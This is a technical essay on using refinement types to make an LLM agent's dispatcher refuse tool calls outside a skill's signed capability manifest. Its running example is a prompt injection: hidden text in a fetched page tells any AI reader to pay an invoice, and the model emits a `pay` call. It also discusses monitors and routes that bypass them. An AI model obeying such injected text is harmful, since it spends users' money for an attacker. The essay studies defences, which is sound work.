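# Refinement types for LLM tool calls: enforcing declared capabilities at dispatch

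## Tool calls, declared capabilities and refinement types

A large language model (LLM) produces text, so it needs other software to send an email or read a file. An LLM agent combines the model with such software. The model emits structured requests, called tool calls, and a program outside the model, called the dispatcher, carries out or refuses each one.

Before a program runs, a type checker reads its source code and rejects code that passes a string to a function that takes a number. A refinement type adds a logical condition to an ordinary type, so a function can require, for example, a number between 1 and 99. Alfredo Metere's *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (May 2026) proposes putting such a type on the dispatcher, so that a tool call goes through only if the permission it needs is on a list that someone signed beforehand.

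Type checkers reason about program text, but tool-call requests come from a model whose output is unpredictable. Whether this is a problem depends on which piece of software the checker examines, so this section explains the mechanics first.

### One turn of an agent

The developer documentation for Claude, in Anthropic's *How tool use works*, describes the cycle that most agents follow. The application sends the model the user's message together with a list of tools. Each tool has a name, a description and a schema, which lays down the fields and types of its arguments. If the model's reply contains a tool call, the reply ends with a stop reason of `tool_use` and includes a small block of JSON, a common text format for structured data. A call to fetch a web page might look like this:

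```json
{
  "type": "tool_use",
  "id": "toolu_01",
  "name": "fetch_page",
  "input": { "url": "https://docs.example.com/guide.html" }
}
```

At this point the block is only text. The model, in Anthropic's words, "never runs anything on its own", so application code reads the name, finds the matching function and runs it on the arguments. The code puts the output into a result block with the same identifier, in the format that Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* specifies, and sends the whole conversation back to the model with the result at the end. The model may then make another tool call, and the process repeats until a reply arrives with a different stop reason.

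The dispatcher is the code in the middle of that loop, and it usually belongs to the developer. However, Anthropic's own servers run web search and a few other tools, and they usually finish the work before the developer's program sees the call, so a check in the developer's dispatcher comes too late for those tools. The Model Context Protocol, an open standard for connecting models to tools, has the same pattern under other names. A client sends a `tools/call` request and a server answers it.

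A dispatcher can be as simple as a table from names to functions, a lookup and a function call. Given the same call, policy and state, it does the same thing every time. The model's output can vary because it is sampled, and it depends on everything in the input, including any page the model has just read. Metere therefore treats the model as a source of arbitrary tool calls and does not try to describe its internals. The scheme requires only that the runtime (the dispatcher and the code around it) can intercept every tool call before it reaches a host API, meaning the functions through which a program accesses files, networks and accounts. This requirement concerns the runtime's source code, which both people and a type checker can examine.

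Some checking of tool calls already happens at this boundary. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* describes an API option that restricts the model's sampling so that the arguments always fit the schema and the name is always one of the tools on offer. Without it, a booking tool that expects `passengers: 2` may receive `"two"`. The option is useful, but it mostly guarantees the shape of a call. The schema for `fetch_page` only requires `url` to be a string, so it accepts the address of an attacker's server. A developer could list the permitted values in the schema as an enumeration, but a schema describes a tool, and which uses of the tool are acceptable depends on the agent's job. Metere makes the same distinction for the Model Context Protocol and OpenAI's function calling, which both validate field names, types and enumerated values but do not tie a call to a set of declared permissions.

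A dispatcher normally reports a refused call by returning a result block with the field `is_error` set to true and a sentence of explanation. The model then continues with that text in its input. Anthropic says Claude will typically retry an invalid request two or three times with corrections. A refusal therefore stops one call but leaves the session running, and the model can still emit something else.

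### Capabilities and manifests

Here, a capability is a named permission, such as `net.egress(host)` for contacting a host over the network or `fs.read(path)` for reading files under a path. Most writing about AI uses the word for what a model is able to do, such as finding a bug in a program. In computer security, an object capability is an unforgeable value inside a program, and holding it is itself the permission, so a function without a reference to the payment object cannot pay. By contrast, any model can output the name of a permission, such as `pay`, but the name has no effect until some code compares it with a list.

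The list comes with a skill, which is a package of instructions, scripts and reference material that an agent loads for a particular kind of job. A skill is usually built around a file named `SKILL.md`. In Metere's companion paper, *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026), every skill has a signed manifest. The manifest's `caps` field holds the declared set D, a finite set of capabilities from a fixed vocabulary. Other fields record the signer, a version number, a security label and how far the skill has been verified.

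The runtime checks the signature, the signer's authority and the rest of the manifest at start-up, before it reads any outside input, and aborts the load if any check fails. After that, the loaded skills stay fixed for the session, and the agent cannot add an entry to D. D is therefore constant, as a type requires, by the time a hostile web page could reach the model. The signature shows who endorsed the skill, but Metere stresses that it does not show that the skill behaves as the manifest claims.

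Metere's worked example is a skill with the name `summarise-fetched-html`. It declares two capabilities:

```
D = { net.egress(*.example.com), fs.read(./.cache/) }
```

Its one script, in Python, fetches a page from a host under example.com, saves the page to a cache directory and reads it back to summarise it. (Saving the page needs a write permission that D lacks. The omission sits inside the script, where a check on tool calls does not reach.)

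Suppose now that one of the fetched pages contains a line, perhaps in white type on a white background, telling any AI assistant that reads it to settle an invoice. This is prompt injection: text in a model's input that redirects it to an attacker's purpose. The route is one of the three in Metere's threat model, a payload that arrives through a document which a harmless skill told the agent to summarise. The payment comes from Metere as well, as the standard illustration of a call that should never get through. Nobody has tampered with the skill and its signature is still valid. The model reads the page, as it must to do its job, and may emit this:

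```json
{
  "type": "tool_use",
  "id": "toolu_02",
  "name": "pay",
  "input": { "token": "USDC", "amount": 500 }
}
```

The `pay` call is well-formed JSON and fits a schema that expects a token and an amount. If the runtime offers no payment tool in this session, strict mode alone makes the call impossible, so an operator who can leave the tool out probably should. But a runtime that serves several skills from one list of tools has to offer `pay` whenever any of them needs it. The call is then wrong only because no entry in D, the skill's declared capabilities, covers it. A fetch from a host outside example.com is a subtler case, because the skill does use the network and only the argument falls outside D. A refined dispatcher, whose input type admits only calls with a capability in D, should refuse both calls.

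### What a refinement type is

An ordinary type such as `int` rules out very little. In their tutorial *Refinement Types*, Jhala and Vazou (2020) list mistakes that a normal type checker misses because the value has the right type: an integer divisor that is zero, an array index beyond the end of the array, and a date whose day does not exist in its month.

A refinement type adds a condition on the content. The notation is

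```
{x : T | p(x)}
```

which reads "the values x of type T for which p(x) is true". So `{x : int | 0 ≤ x}` is the type of non-negative integers. A function that looks up an element of an array `a` can demand an index of type `{i : int | 0 ≤ i ∧ i < length(a)}`, where `∧` means "and". Code that calls the function with an index that might be out of range then fails to compile.

To decide which calls are safe, the checker uses subtyping. Suppose a function requires an integer up to 100, and some code passes it an integer whose type says that it lies between 0 and 50. Every value of the argument's type meets the function's requirement, so the call is safe. The checker turns that observation into a formula:

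```
for every integer x:  (0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ 50)  ⇒  x ≤ 100
```

This is the verification condition for the call. In general, `{x : T | p(x)}` is a subtype of `{x : T | q(x)}` when p(x) implies q(x) for every x of type T, given the facts the checker has recorded about the other variables in scope.

An SMT solver settles the implication. The letters stand for "satisfiability modulo theories", and the solver takes a formula over numbers, sets, strings and similar things and searches for values that make it true. To test an implication, the checker asks for a counterexample, something that satisfies the left side and violates the right:

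```
0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ 50 ∧ x > 100
```

No integer does that, so the formula is unsatisfiable, the implication is valid, and the code passes. If the code instead passes an integer up to 100 to a function that requires one from 0 to 50, the solver can return x = 75, and the checker rejects the call. It does so even if the program would never actually pass 75, because the types do not exclude that value.

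A solver cannot decide every formula. Jhala and Vazou restrict their conditions to a fragment of logic that the solver can always decide, partly so that programmers whose code fails to check need not wonder whether the solver's search strategy caused the failure. The verification languages Dafny and F\* allow richer formulas and rely on solver heuristics for them.

All this assumes that the checker has a useful fact about the argument to start from. For a value that arrives while the program is running, typed at a keyboard or sent over a network, it has none. The fact has to come from a test in the code. An example in *Gradual Liquid Type Inference* (2018) shows how. A function `isPos` takes an integer x and returns a Boolean b, with the type

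```
isPos : x:Int → {b : Bool | b ⇔ 0 < x}
```

so b is true exactly when x is positive. Division, in this example, accepts only positive divisors. The checker goes through the code and generates one subtyping constraint for each division. In the branch that runs when `isPos x` has returned true, a division by x gives rise to this verification condition:

```
((b ⇔ 0 < x) ∧ b)  ⇒  0 < x
```

The solver confirms that it holds for every x, so the checker approves the division without information about the value of x. If a programmer later deletes the test, the premise disappears, the solver finds the counterexample x = 0, and the program no longer compiles. Like x, a tool call from a model is a value that is unknown until it arrives.

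Conditions can also concern sets. *Refinement-Types Driven Development* (Domínguez and Spiwack, 2025) uses Liquid Haskell, a plugin that adds refinement types to Haskell and translates the standard test for set membership into the solver's theory of sets. The example with 50 and 100 then carries over to permissions. Ignoring hosts and paths, a value c with the type `{c : Cap | c ∈ {net.egress, fs.read}}` is acceptable wherever a function takes any of `net.egress`, `fs.read` and `pay`, because the first set is a subset of the second. If a value typed with the larger set is passed to a function that accepts only the smaller one, the solver returns the counterexample c = `pay` and the checker rejects the code.

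Liquid Haskell does not check the membership function, which comes from an outside library, but assumes that its signature is correct. Domínguez and Spiwack warn that a wrong assumption of this kind can let faulty programs through, with consequences as serious as security holes.

### Where the idea comes from

The term "refinement type" dates from a 1991 paper by Tim Freeman and Frank Pfenning on the programming language ML. According to Clancy's *Refinement Types, Annotated Bibliography*, the problem they addressed was that the compiler reported missing cases that could never arise. Their refinements contained no arithmetic. In Freeman's thesis, *Refinement Types for ML* (1994), the programmer declares a finite number of subsets of a data type, such as lists of length zero, one, and two or more, and the checker works out which subset each expression falls into. Because the number of subsets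 is finite, the checker always finishes.

*Liquid Types* (Rondon, Kawaguchi and Jhala, 2008) made conditions on numbers much easier to use. Earlier systems could prove array accesses safe, but programmers had to write most of the conditions themselves. Rondon and colleagues gave the checker a small set of simple predicates and had it find combinations that made the verification conditions true. On a set of OCaml benchmark programs, this cut manual annotation from 31% of the program text to under 1%. That result is for array bounds, where a few stock predicates cover much of what is needed, and it may not carry over to permissions. In *Semantic Subtyping with an SMT Solver* (2010), Bierman, Gordon and colleagues interpreted types directly as logical formulas and defined subtyping as valid implication between them.

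Work on refinement types covered permissions well before it covered agents. In *Bounded Refinement Types*, Vazou, Bakst and Jhala refined Haskell's IO type to track which capabilities a computation uses. The code using those capabilities was also written in Haskell, so the checker could analyze all of it. When a language model is the caller, only the dispatcher's side of the exchange is program code that a checker can analyze.

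## The type of a dispatcher that accepts only declared capabilities

An unrefined dispatcher has the type `Envelope → Result`. It takes any tool call, once the runtime has parsed the JSON, and returns some result. Metere narrows the input:

```
dispatch_M : {e : Envelope | cap(e) ∈ M.caps} → Result
```

In words, `dispatch_M` takes a tool call e whose capability is on the manifest's list, and returns a result.

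The subscript M is the loaded skill's manifest, so the formula describes a family of functions, one per manifest. `Envelope` is the ordinary type underneath, a record that holds an operation, its arguments and the model's stated reason for the call. The function `cap` maps a tool call to the permission it needs. It has to use the operation and the arguments, because the model could write anything in a field labelled "capability". `M.caps` is the declared set D. Plain membership is slightly too strict, because the summariser declares `net.egress(*.example.com)` and fetches from `docs.example.com`, so `∈` has to mean "matches an entry of". The code below ignores hosts and paths and compares only names.

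`Result` carries no condition. The type restricts what goes into the dispatcher, and it has no place for a refusal, because undeclared calls are outside the function's domain. Some other piece of code has to turn them away. Metere describes that piece separately, as a function π that takes any output y of the model:

```
π(y) = cap(y)   if cap(y) ∈ D
π(y) = ⊥        otherwise
```

The symbol ⊥ stands for a refusal. A working runtime needs both π, which takes any input and can refuse it, and `dispatch_M`, which takes only calls that have passed the test and carries them out.

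The condition depends only on `cap` and `M.caps`, so no human can approve an exception. Metere's companion paper is inconsistent about whether exceptions are allowed. In one passage, the gate denies every undeclared capability. In another, if a skill's signer has vouched for its manifest, an undeclared, irreversible call may go to a human who can allow it. An operator who wants such exceptions has to widen the type, perhaps to `{e | cap(e) ∈ M.caps ∨ approved(e)}`, and trust the code that computes `approved`.

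### One proof for all manifests, or one type per skill

In a language with refinement types, the manifest can simply be another argument:

```
dispatch : m:Manifest → {e : Envelope | cap(e) ∈ caps(m)} → Result
```

The condition on the second argument refers to the first. Liquid Haskell allows this, and Domínguez and Spiwack use it throughout their case study to relate one argument to another. The checker treats the manifest m as an unknown, so a successful check covers every manifest, including those of skills not yet written. Developers check the runtime once, when they build it. Loading a skill only supplies a value for m and requires no new check.

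The path that Metere calls simplest, and deployable today, generates a new type for each skill instead. It uses TypeScript, a typed version of JavaScript. For the summariser the generated type might be:

```typescript
type DeclaredCap = "net.egress" | "fs.read";
```

TypeScript types can't state conditions about set membership, but a union of string literals can express the same restriction when D is finite. At start-up, the runtime generates this union from the manifest and compiles the dispatch code against it. Each compilation checks the code for only one D, so the code must be recompiled when the manifest changes, and the production machine needs a compiler. The generator also becomes part of the trusted base (the components that must be correct for the guarantee to hold), because a bug that added `"pay"` to the union would let the dispatcher accept an undeclared capability without an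 error.

A generated type does catch one mistake earlier: a hard-coded call in the runtime's own source to a tool the manifest doesn't declare. If that source calls `pay`, say to settle a usage fee, compiling it against the summariser's type produces an error at load time. If the manifest m is passed as an argument instead, the checker cannot determine whether m includes `pay`, so the programmer has to put a test around the call, and the call is refused only when that line runs.

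TypeScript does much worse with calls that arrive as text, which are the ones that matter. Its standard JSON parser returns a value of type `any`, which the compiler accepts as every other type. So `dispatch(JSON.parse(text))` compiles against the generated type without any test of the parsed value. A developer can instead give the value the stricter type `unknown` and write a guard function to narrow it, but the compiler doesn't check that the guard tests what it claims to test. Even a guard whose body is just `return true` compiles. The generated union therefore constrains the calls that programmers write by hand, but the model's calls are checked only if programmers write a correct guard. Liquid Haskell and F\* verify that the guard establishes the type it claims, unless someone bypasses the verification with an unchecked assumption.

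Neither design specifies which manifest applies to a given call. A runtime that has loaded both the summariser and a billing skill holds two manifests. If the model emits a `pay` call `e` while summarising a hostile page, `dispatch billing e` still type-checks once `e` passes the test against the billing manifest. Metere lists leakage between skills among the attacks the scheme eliminates, reasoning that each skill's dispatcher is bound to its own manifest. But the envelope has no field that names a skill, so the runtime has to work out which skill a call belongs to, and the type does not check that decision.

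### The dispatcher in code

Here is the general form, sketched in the style of Liquid Haskell. The refined signature sits in a special comment, and `IO Result` is the return type of a function with side effects. The sketch omits the data type declarations and an annotation that makes `cap` available in conditions.

```haskell
{-@ dispatch :: m:Manifest
             -> {e:Envelope | member (cap e) (caps m)}
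             -> IO Result @-}
dispatch :: Manifest -> Envelope -> IO Result
dispatch _ e = runTool (op e) (args e)

handle :: Manifest -> Text -> IO Result
handle m txt =
  case parseEnvelope txt of
    Nothing -> return (refuse "malformed tool call")
    Just e
      | member (cap e) (caps m) -> dispatch m e
      | otherwise               -> return (refuse "undeclared capability")
```

`handle` parses the model's text, tests membership, and then either dispatches the call or refuses it. The body of `dispatch` never uses the manifest, which is an argument only so that the condition can refer to it.

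The only line that needs a proof is the one that calls `dispatch`. When the checker reaches it, it has one useful fact, which comes from the signature of `member`: the Boolean that `member` returns is true exactly when the element is in the set. Call that Boolean b. In the accepted branch b is true, so the verification condition is:

```
for every manifest m, tool call e and Boolean b:
  ((b ⇔ cap(e) ∈ caps(m)) ∧ b)  ⇒  cap(e) ∈ caps(m)
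```

This condition has the same shape as the one for dividing by a number that the code has just tested. The solver looks for a counterexample in which b is true, b is equivalent to the membership claim, and the membership claim is false, and it finds none. It can treat `cap(e) ∈ caps(m)` as a single unknown statement, so it needs no information about what `cap` computes or which capabilities the manifest lists. One proof therefore covers all manifests, but the proof would also succeed if `cap` were wrong.

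Now delete the test, so that the second case reads `Just e -> dispatch m e`. The condition loses its left-hand side:

```
for every manifest m and tool call e:
  true  ⇒  cap(e) ∈ caps(m)
```

This is false. One counterexample is the summariser under attack, where `caps(m)` is {`net.egress`, `fs.read`} and `cap(e)` is `pay`. The checker rejects the program, and the build fails.

The checker also rejects subtler mistakes. If a developer adds a debugging switch and changes the test to `debug || member (cap e) (caps m)`, the solver finds a counterexample in which `debug` is true and b is false, so the proof fails. The proof also fails if a later version expands abbreviations in the call after the test and dispatches the expanded call e2. The test establishes that `cap(e)` is in the set, but the dispatch requires the same fact about `cap(e2)`, which the checker cannot derive. Human reviewers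 miss this sort of bug fairly easily because the test is still there, a few lines above.

A runtime might queue tested calls and run them later, or retry one after a network failure. If the queue's elements have the refined type, the code that takes a call out can dispatch it without testing it again. This needs no extra reasoning about queues. *First-Class Refinement Types for Scala* (Bovel, Kunčak and Odersky, 2026) gives the parallel example of a list of non-empty strings, where the ordinary rules for generic types guarantee that any element taken from the list is a non-empty string.

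Their prototype, an extension of the Scala 3 compiler, can also generate the test. In the Haskell sketch, the programmer writes the test and the condition separately, and the solver connects them. In the Scala prototype, a refinement type can serve as a pattern. Their example is `ID`, the type of strings that match a regular expression for identifiers. When a program matches a string against the pattern `id: ID`, the compiled code checks the condition at run time, and inside the matching branch `id` has the type `ID`. A dispatcher written this way would have no hand-written membership test that could become inconsistent with its type.

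### What the compiler has proved

The type checker finishes when someone builds the runtime, perhaps weeks before the summariser fetches the hostile page and the model emits its `pay` call. When that call arrives, the code parses it and computes `cap e`, which is `pay`. `member` returns false, so an ordinary `if` statement stops the payment and `handle` sends back a refusal.

The compiler therefore checks the runtime's source, not the model's call, and proves that no path through the checked code gives `dispatch` a call that has not passed the test. Metere goes further, writing that the types rule out an injected `pay` call before the gate is consulted, and that calling `dispatch_M` with an undeclared envelope is a compile-time error. This is true of calls that programmers write into the source, but it is misleading for calls that arrive from a model. For those, the test in `handle` is the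 gate, and the type only guarantees that the test is there, so the test cannot be removed on the ground that the types already cover it.

The type is more useful in runtimes that call `dispatch` from many places. If the only call is in a ten-line function, a reviewer can quickly see that the test comes first, and the type adds little. But real runtimes tend to accumulate more calls, for retries, batches and sessions that resume after a human's approval. The type checker examines all of them on every build, including any added later.

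### Theorem 2 and its premises

Metere's Theorem 2 states the guarantee. If `dispatch_M` type-checks with the refined input, then no envelope whose capability lies outside `M.caps` can reach a host API through the runtime, whatever the model does. The proof sketch has three steps:

1. The refinement type system is sound, so the checker has verified the condition at every place that calls `dispatch_M`.
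2. The runtime's source contains no route to a host API that bypasses `dispatch_M`.
3. The model can emit any envelope it likes, but only those with a declared capability get through `dispatch_M`, so only those reach a host API.

The argument works, but its hypothesis is too weak as written. It assumes only that `dispatch_M` type-checks. Step 1 needs all of its callers to be checked too, and a checker verifies only the callers it reads. For deployments that want a machine-checkable certificate, Metere suggests porting just the dispatch code to Liquid Haskell or F\* and leaving the rest of the runtime as it is. In the reference implementation, the rest is JavaScript, so a caller can pass any object to the ported code and the checker cannot detect this. The port is safe only if it exposes `handle`, which accepts any input and does its own test, and hides `dispatch` behind it.

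The theorem does not depend on types. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (Bhattarai and Vu, 2026) states almost the same result for a "Command Gate". The model picks an action from a finite vocabulary, a policy checker allows or denies it, and a trusted adapter turns an allowed action into a tool invocation. No sequence of model outputs can then cause a denied action, provided that the checker is deterministic, is not itself a language model, and checks every action before it runs. The paper's theorem covers these conditions with the words "correctly implemented". A refinement checker can mechanically prove part of what that phrase requires. The rest must be assumed, and Theorem 2 has four such premises.

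**The checker is sound.** A checker is sound if it never accepts a program that can violate the conditions in its types. Soundness proofs usually cover a small model of the language. Bovel and colleagues proved soundness in Rocq, a proof assistant that checks each step by machine, but only for a core calculus. Their compiler is a separate prototype with its own solver. Most such languages also have an official way to bypass the check, such as the cast `.asInstanceOf` in Scala, which programmers use at their own risk, or the keyword `assume` in Liquid Haskell. The whole proof in `handle` depends on the signature of `member`, which is one of these assumptions. Domínguez and Spiwack count only such hand-justified code as trusted, excluding compilers and solvers, so a program with a small trusted code base by their definition still depends on a large amount of other software.

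**`cap(e)` has to be the permission that running `e` will actually use.** The solver doesn't check this, as the verification condition showed. If `cap` mapped `pay` to `fs.read`, every proof would still hold and the dispatcher would accept the call to pay the invoice. The type also doesn't constrain the body of `dispatch`, so a body that ignored its argument and paid the invoice every time would type-check. `cap` and the code that runs the tools therefore have to agree.

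**The manifest stays fixed.** If the runtime kept D in a variable that other code could change, a plugin could add `pay` to it, and every later `pay` call would pass the test. An operator could also revoke a capability between the test and the dispatch. Bovel and colleagues show how a compiler can prevent some of this by rejecting any condition that mentions a mutable variable, even `y == x` when x currently holds the right value. The compiler does not yet check that the functions in a condition are free of hidden state, so it would accept a `cap` that read a settings file. In Haskell, the manifest and the tool call are both immutable values. In JavaScript or Python, code can alter the call's arguments after the test unless someone freezes or copies the object first.

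**Every route to a host API goes through the dispatcher.** Security engineers call this complete mediation, an idea that Bhattarai and Vu trace to James Anderson's 1972 reference monitor and a 1975 paper by Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder. Metere calls it a structural invariant, which someone checks once by inspection or with a separate analyser. The refined type does not rule out other routes, although Metere's preprint elsewhere presents it as doing so. A type on `dispatch` constrains only calls to `dispatch`, so code elsewhere in the runtime could still open a network connection directly.

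### Closing the other routes

Domínguez and Spiwack ran into the same limit in code unrelated to security, a compiler routine that replaces variables in a formula. Such a routine has to rename any variable that clashes with one already in use. When they deliberately left out the renaming, Liquid Haskell reported no error and the program gave wrong answers. Their conditions could state which variables belong to which set, but not that a variable may be added only after checking for a clash, since that is a rule about the order of steps. They fixed this with an abstract type, whose internals other modules cannot see. Outside code could extend the set of variables only through one function, which did both the check and the renaming.

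The same technique works for a dispatcher:

```haskell
module Gate (Approved, check, dispatch) where
import HostAPI (runTool)

{-@ data Approved = Ok { man  :: Manifest
                       , call :: {e:Envelope | member (cap e) (caps man)} } @-}
data Approved = Ok { man :: Manifest, call :: Envelope }

check :: Manifest -> Envelope -> Maybe Approved
check m e
  | member (cap e) (caps m) = Just (Ok m e)
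  | otherwise               = Nothing

dispatch :: Approved -> IO Result
dispatch a = runTool (op (call a)) (args (call a))
```

The first line exports the type `Approved` but not `Ok`, the constructor that builds values of that type. Other modules can store an `Approved` value, queue it or pass it on, but they can get one only by calling `check`. The verification condition is unchanged, but it now arises at the line that applies `Ok`.

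The Haskell compiler enforces the export list for all Haskell code, including modules that Liquid Haskell never reads, which closes the gap left by unchecked callers. The refinement covers the few lines inside `Gate`, where the constructor is visible and a careless edit could build an `Approved` value without a test. An `Approved` value also keeps a call together with the manifest it was checked against, so later code cannot pair the call with a different manifest.

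A module could still import `HostAPI` directly. A Haskell package can prevent other packages from doing so by marking `HostAPI` as internal. But this protects only the functions inside `HostAPI`, so any module allowed to perform input and output can import the standard library's file functions instead. JavaScript has the same problem, because a file that cannot import the gate's private functions can still import the platform's file module.

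*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent runtime from Amazon written in Lean 4, a programming language that is also a proof assistant. Every operation that touches files, processes, the network, the version-control system Git or the model takes a token as an argument. The network token is a record of the hosts an agent may reach, and only one module can construct it. When an agent starts, the runtime creates one token for each permission in the agent's grant and none for the rest. These tokens are object capabilities, because code without a network token cannot express a fetch. They also constrain the dispatcher's body, since code written against the network interface alone has no means of making a payment.

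Eisenach and colleagues also supplement private constructors with a linter, a program that searches code for forbidden constructs, which runs on every build. Only modules on a short, named list may access the operating system. In all other modules, the linter rejects file writes, process starts and the construction of tokens. For example, a tool that tries to write directly to `/etc/passwd` does not compile. The linter reads the code after Lean has resolved all names, so an alias or a re-export cannot hide a call.

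Even so, their table of guarantees describes the unforgeability of tokens as "enforced by the build, not proved". The theorems cover the individual checks, such as that the runtime creates a token only for a permission in the grant. The Lean compiler, six small C files that make the system calls, and the Linux kernel remain in the trusted base. This seems about as much assurance as one can currently expect for the fourth premise, and it required designing a whole runtime around that premise. Metere's one-time inspection takes far less work but gives correspondingly less assurance, because the source keeps changing afterwards.

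Some routes, such as web search on the model provider's servers, lie outside the runtime's source, where neither a module system nor a linter can find them. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), which proves theorems about a monitor for agents, lists complete mediation among seven assumptions that a deployment has to meet. A harness meets this assumption if it checks every call and every fetch before executing it, but not if it gives the agent an unmonitored browser or has a retrieval system that carries memories between sessions. Text from such a memory can enter the model's input without any tool call, so a refined dispatcher has no call to test.

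*Agenra* (2026) has a monitor whose core functions have Lean proofs, but it still has to assume that nobody can modify the path from the monitor to the tools. *Kairos* (2026) instead moves the monitor below the runtime. The agent runs inside an isolation layer with no other channel to the outside, and the monitor examines every input and output on the host. This monitor's coverage does not depend on how the agent acts, whereas a monitor at the dispatch layer covers only the actions that an agent declares. The lower monitor would catch a direct network connection that an inspector had missed. The two approaches can be combined, so that isolation supplies the fourth premise and the refined dispatcher ties each call to the manifest.

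## Compile-time proof and run-time check

The proof about `handle` depends on a membership test that runs every time a tool call arrives. Developers need both that test and the type for tool calls from a model, although a rule in Metere's preprint would make them choose between the two.

### The erasure-stable rule

Most compilers delete type information after checking it, which programmers call erasure. In the Haskell sketch of `handle` and `dispatch`, the expression `member (cap e) (caps m)` appears twice. The copy in the signature is part of a comment and is absent from the running program, while the one in `handle` is ordinary code that runs on every call.

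Metere requires the types to be "erasure-stable", meaning that the production runtime must not depend on a run-time check for anything the type system has already proved. On this view, a run-time check that duplicates the type is redundant at best. At worst, a future maintainer removes it "because the types already do it". Developers should therefore keep only one of the two.

The rule makes sense for calls that programmers write into the source. If the runtime always fetches the same status page, a checker can work out the capability from the source, and a run-time test would only repeat the result. The checker lacks this information for calls from a model.

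The refinement type still needs the run-time test in `handle`, because the compile-time proof depends on the result of that test. Without the type, the dispatcher would still reject `pay`, but the compiler would not report an error if someone later deleted the test.

So the rule can only apply to a second test of a call that has already passed the first. Even then, the second test is safe to delete only if the checker has analyzed every caller. The risk of a careless maintainer deleting the test in `handle` is also mainly a TypeScript problem, since that deletion breaks the build in Liquid Haskell.

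### Contracts and hybrid checking

Programming-language researchers worked out how to treat this boundary about twenty years ago. Findler and Felleisen (2002), in *Contracts for Higher-Order Functions*, studied contracts, which are conditions that a program tests while it runs. One of their first examples is a function that takes an integer above 9 and returns one between 0 and 99:

```
f : int [> 9] → int [0,99]
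```

A contract compiler inserts code that tests the argument when something calls `f` and tests the result when `f` returns. A bad argument is the caller's fault, and a bad result is the fault of `f`.

The condition in the dispatcher's refined type can serve unchanged as a contract. If a `pay` call reaches `dispatch`, the program raises an error and blames the caller, the line of runtime code that passed the call on. The model has broken no contract, because `handle` accepts any text. In the logs, a refusal from `handle` is a normal result, but a contract error from `dispatch` means that a programmer forgot a test.

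A contract belongs to the function, so it also checks calls from code that a static checker never analyzes, such as plain JavaScript.

Findler and Felleisen mainly study functions that receive other functions as arguments. In one example, the argument reads a number from a file, and nobody can tell in advance whether the number will be in range. Their system therefore tests each value when the program calls the function. Their practical example comes from the programming environment DrScheme, where plugins register functions that add panels to the preferences window. The contract checks the panels only when the user opens that window. Similarly, if a plugin for an agent runtime is written in an unchecked language and registers a function that produces tool calls on a timer, the runtime cannot approve the function once at registration and has to test every call.

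Flanagan (2006), in *Hybrid Type Checking*, combined run-time tests with refinement types. Suppose a function requires an argument of type T, and some code passes it a value of type S. The checker tries to determine whether every value of type S also has type T, with three possible outcomes:

- It proves that this holds, and accepts the code unchanged.
- It proves that this fails, and rejects the code.
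- It can do neither, perhaps because the condition is too hard or time runs out. It then accepts the code provisionally and inserts a cast, written `⟨S ▷ T⟩`, that tests the actual value at run time.

A hybrid checker would prove the dispatcher's condition and insert no cast if the membership test is in place, but if the test were deleted, it would reject the program instead of repairing it. It inserts a cast, which checks the condition at run time, when the solver can neither prove nor disprove the condition. For example, the runtime might assemble a URL from several strings while the manifest lists hosts by pattern. If the solver cannot determine whether the finished host matches `*.example.com`, the compiled program tests it just before the dispatch.

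Metere's rule describes these inserted casts fairly well, because in a well-typed program they are redundant and never fail. But a test on incoming data must be able to fail, since the model may emit an undeclared call at any time.

Flanagan names two drawbacks of relying on run-time checks alone. They take time, though a set lookup takes almost none compared with a language model's reply. More seriously, they cover only the values and code paths of actual executions, so a defect may appear only after deployment. This matters less for enforcement, because a payment can happen only in an actual execution, but it makes it harder to find the one path where somebody left out the check.

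### What the published implementation checks

The implementation belongs to a framework that Metere (2026), in *enclawed*, describes as a hardened fork of OpenClaw, a personal AI assistant gateway. Its dispatcher is a JavaScript function. `buildRefinedDispatch(M)` takes a manifest and returns a frozen dispatcher that throws a `RefinementError` on any tool call outside D. A minimal function that fits this description is:

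```javascript
function buildRefinedDispatch(manifest) {
  const declared = new Set(manifest.caps);
  return Object.freeze((envelope) => {
    const c = cap(envelope);
    if (!declared.has(c)) throw new RefinementError(c);
    return c;
  });
}
```

In this version, the function copies D when the runtime builds the dispatcher, so later changes to the manifest object have no effect. This is a contract in Findler and Felleisen's sense. The function should refuse the summariser's `pay` call, but it contains no refinement type for a compiler to check. Metere says the implementation needs neither an SMT solver nor a refinement type checker, and offers both as optional replacements. The preprint calls the default "runtime-level refinement checks". A TypeScript library published on Deno uses the word similarly, giving the name `Refinement` to a type for functions that test a value at run time.

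A companion function, `methodB`, probes the dispatcher with every capability in the vocabulary instead of producing a proof, and reports a verdict. With the summariser's original manifest, the dispatcher should accept `net.egress` and `fs.read` and throw an error on every other capability, including `pay`, `spawn.proc` and `fs.write.irrev`. The verification package's 53 unit tests, all of which pass, also cover these errors.

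The probe is better than a spot check because it tries every capability name in a finite vocabulary. If the dispatcher's result depends only on the name, the probe is as conclusive as a proof. The runtime repeats the probe when it verifies a skill at start-up, so it can also catch an edit that broke the dispatcher after someone signed the evidence.

A probe cannot try every host and path, because there are infinitely many. The dispatcher's decision might also depend on something other than the call. If the dispatcher contained a debugging switch that bypassed the test, the probe would pass whenever the switch was off, while a refinement checker would consider both settings and reject the code. Because the probe calls only the dispatcher, it also misses code elsewhere in the runtime that reaches a host API directly.

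The evidence file for this step is named `types.proof`, and in Metere's worked example it contains the derivation that the type checker accepted. The default implementation has no type checker, so the file can presumably contain only the probe's verdict. Together with the other evidence, the file can raise a skill to the top verification level, and the runtime then stops asking a human to approve the skill's declared irreversible calls. An operator deciding whether to allow that should know that this part of the evidence comes from a test.

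### Why TypeScript gives weaker assurance

Metere counts TypeScript's branded types as a limited form of refinement. A brand is an imaginary property that marks a value as having passed some test:

```typescript
type Declared = Envelope & { readonly __brand: "declared" };

function admit(e: Envelope, caps: Set<string>): Declared | null {
  return caps.has(cap(e)) ? (e as Declared) : null;
}
```

If the dispatcher accepts only `Declared` values, a programmer who passes it an ordinary `Envelope` gets a compile error. This catches honest mistakes, but the compiler doesn't check that the brand means what it is supposed to mean. If someone changes the test to `!caps.has(cap(e))`, `admit` approves exactly the wrong calls and the program still compiles. Liquid Haskell would reject the equivalent edit because the refinement type includes the condition.

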